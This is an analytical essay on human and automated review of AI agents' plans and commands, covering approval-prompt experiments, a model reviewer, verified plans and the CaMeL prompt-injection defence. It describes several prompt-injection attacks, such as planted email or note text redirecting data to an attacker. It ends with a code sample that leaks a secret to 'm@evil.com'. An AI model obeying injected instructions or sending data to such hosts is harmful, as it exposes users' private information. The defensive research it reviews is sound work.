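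The preference for AgentSPEX may also be due in large part to its English instructions. A deterministic check can confirm that the steps come in a valid order and that each has the input it needs, but it can't determine what "write a report based on these findings" requires. If people find the plan readable because of the English, then they and deterministic checks rely on different parts of it.

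### The missing comparison of code and prose

A direct test of the reading view would give one group a plan in code and another group the same plan in prose, with the same faults in both, and count the faults each group finds. A limited search found no such experiment. Ghosh and colleagues used only prose, and the large literature on code comprehension mostly studies code. *40 Years of Designing Code Comprehension Experiments* (2022) lists 95 studies from 1979 to 2019 that measured how well people understand code. *Evaluating Code Readability and Legibility* (2021) reviews readability experiments, all of which compare different ways of writing code.

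*Studying the Difference Between Natural and Programming Language Corpora* (2018) summarises evidence that people tend to read prose from start to finish but jump around in code, and that programmers process code less fluently than ordinary language. This suggests that code takes more effort to read, but not that readers miss more faults in it. Someone who has to read a plan slowly because it is written in code might notice something that she would have skimmed over in prose.

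The experiment should compare code with both a short and a detailed prose version of the plan, because prose usually leaves out details that code has to include. Nobody could find the wrong date test in the prose version of the invoice plan, since it says only "from last month". A more detailed version could say that the agent will move every file last changed in September. That sentence contains the same fault as the code, and a user who can't program would probably have a better chance of spotting it there. If code beat only the short version, its advantage would come from the extra detail, which prose can also supply.

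### Goals, corrections and responsibility

A person who reads a plan can notice that it serves the wrong goal even if it satisfies its specification, which a deterministic check cannot do. The studies give this modest support. Ten of Kumar and colleagues' 24 participants changed the first plan, and *Babysitting AI Agents* paraphrases a user who spent a long time reviewing a plan because the agent kept proposing unnecessary parts, including a new email service when one already existed. But the spreadsheet plans were in prose, so they are evidence for showing people a plan, not for writing it in code. The agent's questions also drew out about five times as many new requirements as the plan did, and an agent can ask questions whether or not it plans in code.

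Reading a plan also lets people correct it before it runs. Kumar and colleagues' participants did this mostly by telling the agent what to change, which requires them to know what they want but not how the plan works. Changing a code plan by hand also requires understanding how it works. In Balepur and colleagues' follow-up task, students who understood their code better were better at extending it, even after the researchers controlled for how complete the code had been at the start.

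There is least evidence on whether reading a plan enables someone to answer for it. A person who approves a plan may later have to explain why, and the students who used the agent often couldn't say what a piece of their own code was for. None of these experiments asked people to justify an approval. The nearest measure is in the spreadsheet study, where 16 of the 24 participants felt creatively responsible for the workbook they had made in Plan Mode, compared with 14 in Act Mode. The difference is small, and feeling responsible for a budget's design doesn't show that someone could explain why an agent deleted the wrong files.

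## A dangerous command shown to 1,053 people and to a model reviewer

People who supervise coding agents read whole plans only occasionally. Much more often, they approve or reject a single command that the agent shows them before running it. Claude Code, the coding agent of the AI company Anthropic, has a manual mode for this. According to Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode*, the agent in this mode stops before most actions that edit files, run commands or use the network.

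A command like this is a code plan of one line. For the invoice job it might be:

```
mv /invoices/2026-09-*.pdf /archive/
```

`mv` moves files, and the asterisk stands for any text, so the command moves every PDF whose name begins with 2026-09. A user who knows the notation can see which files will move and where they will go. But, as with `move` in the longer plan, the line doesn't show what happens to a file already in the archive with the same name.

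Some commands reveal even less. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026), an analysis of 290 incident reports, gives the example of `python3 setup.py`. This routine-looking command runs whatever code is in `setup.py`, which the approval prompt doesn't show. Uninformative prompts contributed to 31 of the incidents. In 80 incidents, the user had let the agent act without asking, often to avoid answering hundreds of prompts in a session.

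Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* (2026) uses the term "approval fatigue" to describe how people who keep answering approval prompts stop paying close attention after clicking "approve" enough times. Auto mode replaces these prompts with a model reviewer, which Anthropic compared with people in an experiment published in August 2026.

### The experiment

According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), a research vendor recruited 1,053 paid testers for a coding study. The testers worked in an environment built for the study, not on their own projects. They knew they were being evaluated, but not which behaviour mattered. Partway through each session, the text of one prompt was replaced with a clearly dangerous command, and the vendor recorded whether the tester approved it. Only the text changed, so approving the command did no damage.

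The testers refused the command in 143 sessions (13.6%). The model reviewer blocked 937 of the same 1,053 commands (89.0%). Anthropic also gives the number that only one of them caught, which is enough to work out the rest:

| | Model blocked | Model allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Person refused | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Person approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

The model missed 116 commands, and the testers refused 6 of those, an added catch rate of 5.2%. Adding the testers as a second reviewer raises the share of commands caught from 89.0% to 89.6%. The model blocked 800 of the 910 commands that the testers approved, an added catch rate of 87.9%.

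If the testers and the model had missed commands independently, the testers would have refused 13.6% of the 116, or about 16. They refused 6. A gap that large would occur by chance in fewer than one in a hundred such studies, assuming the sessions are independent of each other. The most likely explanation is that some of the commands looked harmless to both the testers and the model. In Ghafouri's hospital experiment, by contrast, model reviewers caught about 90% of the errors that a rule-based checker had missed.

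Anthropic doesn't say how many different commands it used, though, so the sessions may not be independent cases. If it used only about twenty, two or three of them could account for most of the model's 116 misses, and the 5.2% would mainly reflect how harmless those few looked.

The testers' refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while the model's rate stayed flat. Approval fatigue could explain the drop, but people who click quickly are also more likely to reach a fiftieth prompt, so the later group may include more people who never read carefully. Fatigue within a session can't be the main reason for the low overall rate, since about five in six testers approved the dangerous command even near the start. If all the testers had refused at the early rate, and their misses had been unrelated to the model's, they would have caught about 20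 of the 116 cases the model missed, raising the combined catch rate to only 90.9%.

### Why the testers may have approved

The vendor recorded whether testers approved the command, not whether they noticed what it would do. A tester who noticed that a command would delete a folder might still have approved it, because the folder wasn't hers and she assumed a paid study wouldn't let her do real harm. At work she would have her own files to protect and would know which ones mattered. These differences could make testers approve more dangerous commands than they would at work. Other differences could make them approve fewer, because people usually take more care when they know someone is evaluating them, and the commands were clearly dangerous, while real mistakes are often subtle. The study can't separate these effects.

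It is also unclear how much the testers knew about shell commands. The article calls them professional testers, but its chart caption, quoted in Willison's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), calls them developers.

Anthropic was studying its own product and published the results in the announcement that auto mode would become the default on most plans. It doesn't report how often the model reviewer blocked harmless commands, which makes the 89% hard to judge. The closest figure comes from a customer, the software company Gusto, where about 10% of sessions included at least one block, but Anthropic doesn't say how many were mistakes.

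The experiment also lacks a comparison with deterministic checks. If the commands were as clearly dangerous as Anthropic says, a list of forbidden patterns might have stopped many of them. Claude Code already detects some commands that delete critical folders, and users can't write a rule that approves these in advance. A pattern list would miss `python3 setup.py`, where the danger is in another file. The experiment is good evidence that a model reviewer is better than inattentive people at reading commands, but it doesn't show how much of that advantage a conventional program could match.

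### People with more reason to look

People did much better in a smaller experiment, reported in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026). Its 113 participants, all from outside the software industry, supervised an AI assistant through a simulated day of 18 actions. Seven of these went beyond what the user had asked for, such as reading private messages or buying a $25 airport lounge pass. The prompts described each action in plain language. The 34 people who had to approve every action blocked 59.6% of the overreaching actions and still let through 94% of those the task required.

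The gap between 59.6% and 13.6% may not be due to plain language, because the two studies differ in almost everything else. In Yan's study, more than a third of the actions were out of bounds, which gives people a reason to keep reading, and nobody had to answer more than 18 prompts. Participants had also just answered questions about which actions of this kind they would allow. Some of their approvals weren't mistakes. About 88% approved an unrequested call to the airport to confirm the flight, which many users would welcome, while only 21% approved a public post announcing that the user was travelling.

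Another 44 people in Yan's study saw ten prompts instead of 18 because a model had already allowed eight harmless actions. The model left the other ten for them to decide, including all seven that went too far. They approved those seven 46% of the time, compared with 40% among people who decided on all 18. So seeing fewer prompts didn't make people stricter.

The total of 89.6% assumes that a refusal by either the person or the model reviewer stops the command. In auto mode, after a block, the agent usually finds a safer way to proceed or asks the user for permission. After three blocks in a row or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to manual approval. If the user can overrule the model, a dangerous command is stopped only when both refuse it. In Anthropic's experiment, both refused 137 commands, or 13%. Users would probably look harder at a prompt that follows a block than the testers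 did at theirs, but Yan's result suggests that they would still approve many such prompts.

### What a better prompt adds

Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, changed what the prompt shows. In one of their examples, a user allows an agent to send only summary totals to an auditor. The agent copies raw invoice rows into a file called `report.csv`, then asks to send it to the auditor. The auditor is an approved recipient and the agent is allowed to send files, so nothing in the request looks wrong. To see the problem, the reader has to know where the file's contents came from and what the user originally said.

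The researchers gave 80 volunteers 12 requests each, half of them unsafe, on one of four kinds of screen:

| What the screen showed | Unsafe requests refused | Harmless requests refused | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description of the action | 45.0% | 8.3% | 16 seconds |
| The exact details of the action as well | 56.7% | 10.0% | 23 seconds |
| Also the user's instructions and a log of earlier steps | 67.5% | 12.5% | 39 seconds |
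| The same facts, with the combined effect stated in a sentence | 75.8% | 14.2% | 33 seconds |

The exact details correspond most closely to code, and they raised the refusal rate by about 12 points. The instructions and the log, which no command contains, added another 11. The effect of moving from a log to a plain statement of what the command does is the least certain. After adjustment, the difference favoured the statement by 7.9 points, with an interval from 20 points in its favour to 4 points against it. Only 20 people saw each screen, and the researchers hadn't registered their analysis in advance.

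Half the requests were unsafe, so these volunteers had even more reason for suspicion than Yan's participants. Their results are closer to an upper limit than to what a busy user would manage, but they show that people can do better than 13.6%. If a reader caught three-quarters of the commands that Anthropic's model missed, the share caught would rise from 89% to about 97%. However, the commands the model missed may be the hardest to catch, as the testers' results suggest, so it is unknown whether any reader could do this.

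Trying harder doesn't guarantee that people will find the defects either. In Dissanayake and colleagues' study, people tested the agent's code but often missed its hidden defects. They were about equally confident on every task, although they found far more defects on some than on others. So a careful reader may not know when she has looked carefully enough.

### Commands and plans in everyday use

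Anthropic also reports that outside the experiment, users approve 97% of permission prompts, up from the 93% it reported in March 2026. Most commands are harmless, so even a perfect reviewer would approve nearly all of them, and the high approval rate alone doesn't show that users aren't reading. The experiment is better evidence because the right answer there was to refuse.

By June 2026, 49.5% of active users of the command-line version had written a rule that lets some shell commands run without a prompt. Many of these rules cover every command that starts with `python`, which is almost the same as allowing everything. A quarter of interactive sessions start with permission prompts switched off. For these users, a model reviewer doesn't replace a human one, because no person was reading the commands.

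Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed 115 more about such decisions. They warn that someone who repeatedly approves the same kind of action may be tired of being asked rather than happy with the action. A tool that turns repeated approvals into a standing rule could therefore permanently allow actions that the person approved without paying attention.

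Developers who read code carefully aren't always careful with commands. Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), in *From Delegation to Action Approval*, surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents, and about half said they carefully reviewed most or all of the code their agents wrote. Of these, 61% often approved at least one type of action without close review, compared with 67% of the others, a difference that could easily be due to chance. But developers who inspected diffs, which show line by line what changed in a file, were less likely to approve destructive commands without looking. The answers are self-reported, so the true figures may be worse.

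Users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code presents for approval, compared with 3% of its permission prompts. An optimistic explanation is that people study a plan carefully because it covers the whole task and arrives before they are tired. The way plans are displayed may also help. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), a survey of approval designs, finds that plans and previews of file edits give reviewers the most information, while most approval prompts in real products show a raw command on a single line.

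But a rejected plan needn't contain a fault. According to Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode*, a user can approve a plan or choose "No, keep planning" and tell the agent what to change. So a rejection is often a request for another draft, perhaps because the user prefers a different library or wants fewer steps. One task can also produce several rejections. If every task ended with an approved plan, a 39% rejection rate would mean an average of 1 / 0.61, or about 1.6, drafts per task.

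Plans also give people more to object to than commands do. A command that lists the files in a folder leaves little to disagree with, while a plan for a new feature involves many choices. People who ask for a plan have also already decided they want to review one, so they may be more careful than people who click through prompts.

Wu and colleagues' survey suggests that many of the objections are about the agent's direction or approach. The most common reason developers gave for intervening was that the agent had misunderstood the task or gone in the wrong direction (65%), followed by a wrong or overcomplicated approach (54%). Only 34% mentioned a risky or destructive command. Salerno and colleagues want tools to distinguish refusing one action from ruling out a whole approach, since a user who refuses a command may only want the agent to reach the same goal another way.

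The 39% is therefore good evidence that many people read plans and use them to steer the agent. It isn't evidence that they would catch a dangerous step, because nobody planted dangerous steps in those plans. It also gives little support to code plans in particular, because the plans people send back are mostly in ordinary language, while the commands they readily approve are code. Plans and commands also differ in length, timing and number, which could fully explain why people respond to them differently.

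### Harm in real sessions

Anthropic's last comparison uses sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged for review, all from users who had agreed to let the company analyse their data. A model graded each session for the severity of any harm and for how explicitly the user had asked for the action. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for, such as deleting rows from a live database, occurred in 6.3% of flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. The rate was also higher with manual approval at every other level of severity that Anthropic tested.

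Here real users had real files at stake, which answers one objection to the experiment. But they chose the mode themselves, and Anthropic recommends manual mode for sensitive work and unfamiliar code. If they follow that advice, manual sessions will contain more serious harm even if both kinds of review work equally well.

The percentages also depend on how many sessions the safety systems flag. Suppose each mode has 1,000 sessions, 6 of which contain serious harm. If the systems flag 95 manual sessions and 250 auto mode sessions, including all the harmful ones, then 6.3% of flagged manual sessions and 2.4% of flagged auto mode sessions contain serious harm, although harm is equally common in both modes. Auto mode lets an agent work longer without interruption, so its sessions might well raise more flags over minor matters. But longer sessions also give an agent more chances to do harm, which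 would make a low rate more impressive. Without the number of sessions in each mode, nobody outside Anthropic can tell which effect is larger.

The grader is another weak point. Anthropic doesn't say which model it used. If that model has the same blind spots as the reviewer, it will miss some of the harm the reviewer let through, and auto mode will look safer than it is.

### When Anthropic still recommends a human reader

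Willison, a software developer who writes about AI tools, accepts that a model reviewer is better than constant prompts, but points out that it misses 11% of dangerous commands. He wants to find practical ways to run agents without access to data or tools that could cause harm. Restricting access is more promising than a second reading for the 110 commands that both the testers and the model let through, because a sandbox can contain a command that nobody has recognised as dangerous.

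Anthropic still recommends that users review the agent's actions themselves for high-stakes changes to production infrastructure, the live systems that a company's customers depend on. This advice is consistent with the experiment if people read a few important commands much more carefully than one prompt among dozens, but the experiment didn't test whether they do.

In Wu and colleagues' survey, the 65 developers who worked on systems where a failure could cause physical, medical or operational harm reported approving actions without close review more often than other developers did, for six of the seven types of action. They may use agents more or be more honest about their habits. But high stakes alone don't make people read closely, so a company that relies on human review for its production systems would do well to test that review, for instance by occasionally inserting a harmless fake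 command that a careful reader should refuse.

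## Deleting two files: a plan checked against a specification

Someone who approves an agent's commands one at a time has to notice every dangerous one herself. Erik Meijer, a programming-language designer who has worked at Microsoft and Meta, would rather rely on proof. In *Guardians of the Agents* (2025), he proposes that the agent write out its whole plan, and that the plan run only if a verifier finds that it meets a specification.

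The agent writes the plan in a restricted format, a JSON list of steps. Each step calls one of a fixed set of tools, names the result and gives the next step. A later step can refer to the fetched emails by name, but the agent doesn't see any emails while planning. Meijer wants a restricted format because he thinks nobody can reason reliably about a language like Python, where importing a library can change what addition does.

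If a plan fails, the agent writes another. In a talk, *Return of the Theorem* (2026), Meijer says that code is now so easy to produce that nothing is lost by throwing a plan away. He gives no measurements of how well agents work under these restrictions.

### Programs that run without a reader

Java and .NET have worked in a similar way for decades. Their compilers turn a program into bytecode, an intermediate form that few people read. Before the bytecode runs, a verifier checks that it uses memory safely, never treats one type of data as another, and respects limits on which parts of the program can use others. Some checks can only happen while the program runs, such as whether it asks for the eleventh item in a list of ten.

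Meijer borrows even more from proof-carrying code, as he acknowledges in another talk, *I've never seen anything scarier than an LLM with tool calls* (2026). Necula and Lee developed it for packet filters in *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking* (1996). Packet filters are small programs that select which incoming network messages to pass to an application. They run fastest inside the kernel, the core of the operating system, where a faulty one could overwrite anything.

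In their scheme, the kernel's designer publishes a safety policy. A filter may read only the message and a small scratch area, write only to the scratch area, and jump only forwards, which guarantees that it finishes. The filter's author attaches a formal proof that the filter obeys the policy. The kernel uses the filter's code to derive a logical statement that the code never breaks the policy, then checks that the attached proof proves it. If someone tampers with the code, the statement usually changes and the old proof no longer proves it, so the kernel accepts altered code only if it is still safe.

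Necula and Lee tried this with four filters of 8 to 47 instructions. Their checker was about five pages of C and took 0.8 to 2.4 milliseconds per filter. Finding the proofs was harder, and their theorem prover sometimes needed a programmer's help. But whoever writes the filter does that work, so the kernel can accept a stranger's filter without anyone reading it.

However, the policy doesn't restrict the filter's answers, so a filter that picks out the wrong messages still passes. Meijer wants his verifier to also establish that a plan does what the user asked.

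### A specification that accepts the wrong plan

In Meijer's example, a user asks an agent to delete two files, `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`. The agent has a tool called `delete_file`, which accepts either a file name or a pattern. It might decide that one call is simpler than two and write this plan, slightly shortened here:

```json
{
  "description": "Delete foo.txt and bar.txt",
  "steps": {
    "callDeleteFile": {
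      "function": "delete_file",
      "arguments": { "file": "*.txt" }
    }
  }
}
```

The call deletes every text file, although the description mentions only two. The description doesn't affect what runs, so the verifier ignores it.

The verifier needs to know what the tool does and what the user wants. Meijer states both as postconditions, which are conditions that must hold after something has run. In words, they are:

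```
delete_file(pattern)
    for every file f: if f matches the pattern, f no longer exists

the request
    foo.txt no longer exists, and bar.txt no longer exists
```

The proof that the plan is correct is short. Both names match `*.txt`, so by the tool's postcondition neither file exists after the call, which is all the request requires. The verifier therefore accepts the plan. If the folder also contained `notes.txt`, the call deletes that file too, but no condition covers it. Meijer doesn't blame the model for this, because the plan meets the specification it was given.

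With the same specification, the verifier also rejects a good plan. Suppose the agent deletes `foo.txt` in one call and `bar.txt` in another. After the first call, the verifier can prove that `foo.txt` is gone, and after the second, that `bar.txt` is gone. But the tool's postcondition doesn't rule out that deleting one file brings another back, so the verifier can't prove that both files are gone at the end, even though no person would worry about this.

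### Saying what must stay the same

McCarthy, the advocate of proofs over testing, described this difficulty with Patrick Hayes in 1969 as the frame problem. To reason about an action, you have to state what it leaves alone as well as what it changes. A frame condition does this. Meijer adds one to the tool:

```
for every file f: if f does not match the pattern,
    f exists after the call exactly if it existed before
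```

He says that the `*.txt` plan then fails, but this condition alone isn't enough. `notes.txt` does match `*.txt`, so the tool's frame condition doesn't protect it. The request needs a frame condition of its own:

```
for every file f other than foo.txt and bar.txt:
    f exists afterwards exactly if it existed before
```

The verifier can now find the fault by searching for a counterexample, which here is a starting folder for which the plan breaks a condition. Meijer uses an SMT solver for this, a program that searches for values that satisfy a set of logical formulas. Any folder containing `notes.txt` is a counterexample, since the plan deletes that file and the request requires it to stay. The verifier rejects the plan even if the user's real folder has no other text files, because the plan has to be correct for every possible folder.

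The two-call plan passes. The first call removes `foo.txt` and leaves everything else as it was. The second removes `bar.txt` and leaves everything else as it was, so `foo.txt` stays deleted and `notes.txt` survives. The two frame conditions do different jobs:

| Frame conditions | Delete `*.txt` | Delete `foo.txt`, then `bar.txt` |
|---|---|---|
| None | Passes | Fails |
| On the tool only | Passes | Passes |
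| On the request only | Fails | Fails |
| On both | Fails | Passes |

A person who knows what the asterisk means could have spotted the fault at once, without being told that other files matter. The verifier could detect it only after someone had written into the specification that other files must not be deleted. From then on, the verifier catches this fault in every plan, including those a tired reader would approve because the description looks right.

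Software could add the frame condition "nothing else changes" to every deletion request by default, so people wouldn't have to write each one themselves. But a condition about which files exist wouldn't stop a plan from emailing the contents of `foo.txt` to a stranger before deleting it. The verifier in an experimental tool called *clauz3* instead lists every call a program could make to certain trusted functions. A rule can then cover a whole kind of action, for instance by banning all email. As its developers explain in normalform-ai's *Background And Related Work*, an action missing from the list can't happen, so they don't need a separate frame condition for it. This works only for the kinds of action that the verifier tracks.

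### Email that leaves the company

Meijer's other example needs a rule about where information goes. A user asks an agent to summarise her emails, and one of them contains instructions to send the summary to an outside address and not to tell her. An ordinary agent reads the emails before it decides what to do next, so it may obey. Under Meijer's proposal, the agent plans to fetch the emails, summarise them and return the summary before it reads any of them, so text in an email can't add a step.

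An attacker could still influence the agent before it writes the plan, for instance by hiding the instructions in the description of the tool that fetches email. The plan might then send the summary to the attacker. To catch this, the company adds a rule that nothing from the inbox may flow into the body of an email to an address outside its domain. A static analyser traces the data from the fetched emails to the summary and then to the outgoing message. It finds a forbidden path, so the plan never runs.

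Writing this rule is easier to justify than writing the frame condition on the deletion request, since the rule applies to every plan that touches email. But it also has to be exactly right. Meijer's printed rule refers to a tool called `fetch_email`, while his first plan calls `fetch_mail`. The slip is harmless in a magazine article, and most readers would skim past it. But a checker that took both names literally would find no path from the inbox in that plan, even if someone added a step that sent the emails to an attacker.

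The rule also can't guarantee that the summary is accurate, because a model writes it when the plan runs and a malicious email might still influence the wording. Meijer's proofs cover what an agent does with its tools. He suggests conventional filters for the wording, and in his later talk he says nobody can write a formal specification of a "safe" answer.

### What people still have to trust

Meijer claims that his approach works "without the need to trust the AI nor any of the artifacts it produces". This is true of the plan and the proof. If a model writes an invalid proof, a sound checker rejects it, however capable or deceptive the model is. But the check only guarantees that the plan meets the specification, so users still have to trust several other things.

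The most important part is the specification itself. In proof-carrying code, the recipient writes the policy, but in *Return of the Theorem*, Meijer has the system turn the user's question into a specification, a step he calls auto-formalization. If a model does this translation, somebody needs to trust or check the result. For example, if the model translates the request to delete two files as "no text files remain", the `*.txt` plan passes with a valid proof. A better checker wouldn't fix this problem, which De Millo and colleagues raised in 1979.

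Retrying makes gaps in the specification more dangerous. An agent that keeps writing plans until one passes will sometimes find a correct plan and sometimes a wrong one that nobody thought to exclude. In the process documented for a tool by ServantSoftware, people review the checks once instead of reviewing everything an agent writes, and they ask what wrong implementation would pass. For the deletion request, a plan that uses `*.txt` would.

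Reviewing the specification instead of the plan saves the most effort when one specification covers many plans. Meijer describes a car dealer's chatbot that a customer persuaded to sell him a car for $1. A rule that no car may sell below its minimum price would block every such deal, so it is worth having several people read it closely. The deletion request's specification, by contrast, covers only one plan, and with the frame condition it is harder to read than the single call it is used to check. A user would be better off reading `*.txt`, unless the software supplies the frame condition and she only has to confirm the two file names.

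Many tasks have no such rules yet. *Symbolic Guardrails for Domain-Specific Agents* (2026) found that 85% of the benchmarks it reviewed had no concrete policies, only broad goals or an appeal to common sense. Where policies did exist, conventional programs could enforce 74% of their requirements. So the lack of written rules may be a bigger obstacle than the limits of the checkers. Miyazono (2025) notes in *Set Laws AI Must Prove It's Following* that few people are trained to write formal rules, though he expects AI to help.

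People also have to trust the descriptions of the tools. The proof about `delete_file` relies on the tool's stated postconditions, not its actual behavior. If the real tool also searches subfolders, or treats `FOO.TXT` as the same file as `foo.txt`, a plan with a valid proof can delete the wrong file. The same problem arises with `move` in the invoice plan if its description doesn't mention overwriting. Tool descriptions are worth human review, given that Basili and Selby's readers found more interface faults than their testers did. An engineer can check each description once for all later plans that use the tool.

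Last, there is the checker, along with the software that carries out the approved plan. Necula says in *Proof-Carrying Code* (1997) that the recipient needs to trust only a simple checking algorithm and the soundness of its own policy. Meijer makes the same point with Sudoku, where solving a puzzle is hard but checking a finished grid is easy. But the tools he suggests for his examples mostly search for the proof or the forbidden path themselves. An SMT solver such as Z3 is much larger than Necula and Lee's five-page checker, so it has more room for bugs that could let a bad plan through. *clauz3* also relies on Z3, and its developers say a possible next step is to have the agent supply a checkable proof.

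In normalform-ai's project, the agent writes a program and states what the program guarantees, for example that it will pay a bill from one account and spend no more than $500. The verifier proves these guarantees, and the user accepts or rejects them without reading the code. normalform-ai describes the engineer who writes the tool descriptions and the vocabulary for guarantees as the "root of trust". So the user reads a few sentences about each task, and an expert reads the parts that many tasks share. An agent can propose weak guarantees, but then the user can see that it is asking for broad permission. However, she can also approve the guarantees as carelessly as she would any other prompt.

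### A readable version of a proven plan

Meijer wants the user to see the plan. In *Guardians of the Agents*, he turns the email plan into a short paragraph of ordinary English with the tool calls in brackets. Because the plan has a fixed structure, a program could produce this text directly from the steps that will run. Text produced this way would be more reliable than the description in the deletion plan, which the agent wrote and got wrong.

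His examples don't quite achieve this. The English version of the first email plan mentions formatting the summary, which isn't a step in the plan. The English version of the malicious plan gives "for compliance purposes" as the agent's reason for sending the summary to the outside address. This excuse came from the attacker, and no tool call contains it. Including the agent's explanations can therefore help an attacker persuade the user, so it would be safer, though duller, to show only the calls and their arguments.

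Once the proof exists, the rendering adds no evidence that the plan obeys the stated rules, but it can still help the user notice a missing rule. If she had read that the system was about to delete every file ending in `.txt`, she could have objected, and someone could then have added the missing frame condition. She might also remember something that no specification contains, as some of Kumar and colleagues' spreadsheet users did.

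The plan can serve this purpose even if she reads it second. normalform-ai's *Guardians Synergies* suggests showing the proven guarantees first and an explanation of the steps below them. She learns from the guarantees what can't happen, and reading the steps gives her a chance to notice that the guarantees leave out something she cares about.

Meijer has become less interested in making plans readable. In spring 2026 he praised his own plan language, Universalis, because it reads like English, and complained that coding agents show users little more than a to-do list. By the summer he was telling an audience that machines write, prove and run these plans, so "we should stop designing languages for humans". That is reasonable for plans if the specification is good enough. But the dealer still has to read the rule about minimum prices to know whether it is the rule he wants, so a formal language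 that looks like English is more useful for specifications than for plans.

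## Python plans run under data-flow rules

Meijer argues that nobody can reason reliably about Python before it runs. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., Google DeepMind, 2025) presents CaMeL, which uses Python for its plans anyway and checks each step as it runs. CaMeL defends against prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in text the agent is only supposed to read, such as an email or a web page.

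### Sending Bob a document

Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains the system with a request from the original paper. A user asks her assistant to send Bob the document he requested at their last meeting, and says that the document's name and Bob's address are in the meeting notes. One model, the planner, sees this request but not the notes. It might write:

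```python
notes = find_notes("last meeting")
name = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob want?", notes)
address = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's address?", notes)
document = fetch_document(name)
send_email(to=address, attachment=document)
```

The second and third lines call a separate quarantined model, which reads the notes but has no tools. If the notes contain a hidden instruction to forward the user's whole inbox, the quarantined model can't carry it out, and the planner never receives it. The notes can affect only the values of `name` and `address`.

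Willison proposed this division of labour in 2023. Debenedetti and colleagues pointed out that an attacker may not need to change the plan. If he can edit the notes, he can replace Bob's address with his own, and the same five-line plan will send him the document.

CaMeL closes this gap with its own interpreter, the program that runs the Python. The interpreter records where each value came from and who may read it, and anything computed from that value inherits the record. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a rule, a short Python function that allows or denies the call. The rule for `send_email` might require a trusted recipient. Bob's address came from the notes, so it doesn't count as trusted by default. If it is on a list of addresses the user trusts, the email goes out. Otherwise, the system can ask her to approve the email.

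Another rule might require that the recipient be allowed to read the attachment. If the attacker changed the document's name instead of the address, this rule would help only if Bob wasn't allowed to read the substituted file.

Unlike most runtime monitors, CaMeL's interpreter needs the plan to be code. An email address doesn't show that it came from the notes, but the interpreter can trace it there because it ran every line that produced it. If one model had read the notes and then chosen the next action, a cautious monitor would have to treat everything it did afterwards as possibly influenced by the notes.

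An agent can also avoid this without writing a complete program. FIDES, the system that *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) builds on, hides untrusted text behind variable names while the agent chooses its tool calls one at a time. So the tracking depends on keeping data separate from instructions, which comes naturally in code but not in prose.

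None of this requires anyone to read the Python. Debenedetti and colleagues chose Python because it is popular and language models write it well. Familiarity with a language helps models as well as people. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) presents a new language for secure agents. In one of its examples, GPT-5.2 needed three attempts to write a factorial function that the interpreter could parse, although the prompt included a summary of the syntax.

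### Attacks stopped and tasks lost

The usual test for such defences is AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, banking, travel and messaging tasks with attacks hidden in the data. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) adapted it for groups of agents that call one another. Attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL and 0.2% when each agent used it. The experiments used no rules for tool calls, so this drop came from separating the planner from the untrusted text.

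Garby and colleagues explain why separation alone works so well. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack in AgentDojo's banking section, the attack requires an action that a plan for the user's task would never contain. For example, if the user asks for a summary of recent transactions, the plan has no line that sends money. The data-flow rules matter in the other 47 combinations, where the plan already contains a call that an attacker could misuse.

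However, CaMeL completes fewer tasks with the rules on. When Garby and colleagues ran it on the banking tasks without them, it completed 67% with one model and 71% with another. With the rules, it completed 37.5% with either model. Attacks succeeded in five of the 622 completed runs without the rules and in none of the 588 with them. In *SecureClaw* (2026), CaMeL stopped all 629 attacks in the whole benchmark but completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks, while the researchers' own system completed 59. The researchers had to adapt CaMeL's code to their set-up, which may have caused it to fail some tasks.

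Kolluri and colleagues think such comparisons overstate the drawbacks of the protection. In a benchmark, an unprotected agent acts as if a user had approved everything, while a protected one fails when a rule blocks it, as if no user were there to give approval. In real products, agents often ask for approval before taking any action with consequences. So the researchers counted how many approvals each agent would need for the tasks it completed. Basic data-flow rules reduced this number by a factor of up to 1.5 without reducing the number of completed tasks. An agent that knew the rules and planned around them needed up to 1.9 times fewer approvals than FIDES.

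These counts assume that the user approves every request and that nobody is attacking. They measure how often she has to answer, but not whether she would notice a bad request. Debenedetti and colleagues list user fatigue as a limitation of CaMeL. Fewer questions may not make her more careful, since Yan's participants were no stricter when they saw fewer prompts. But the interpreter tracks where a suspicious address came from and could show this in the prompt. This kind of information helped Hossain and colleagues' volunteers refuse unsafe requests.

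A system can ask the user fewer questions by asking about data instead of actions. If an email contains a to-do list with ten items, the user can declare the email trustworthy once or approve ten separate actions. Declaring it trustworthy saves time, but a careless decision then applies to all ten actions.

Garby and colleagues let their planner make such declarations in the plan itself, before it has seen any untrusted data. Only two of 1,296 attacked runs went wrong. In both, the user had asked the agent to pay whatever bill a file contained, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Data-flow rules cannot distinguish a real bill from a fake one in that file, so they could only have stopped the attack by refusing the task. A person could at least notice, from one line of the plan, that it relies on the file.

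### Where the tracking stops

CaMeL's interpreter follows only the branch of the plan that actually runs, and Garby and colleagues show how a plan can exploit this to leak a secret. A simplified version of their example is:

```python
rich = True
if account.balance <= 1_000_000:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

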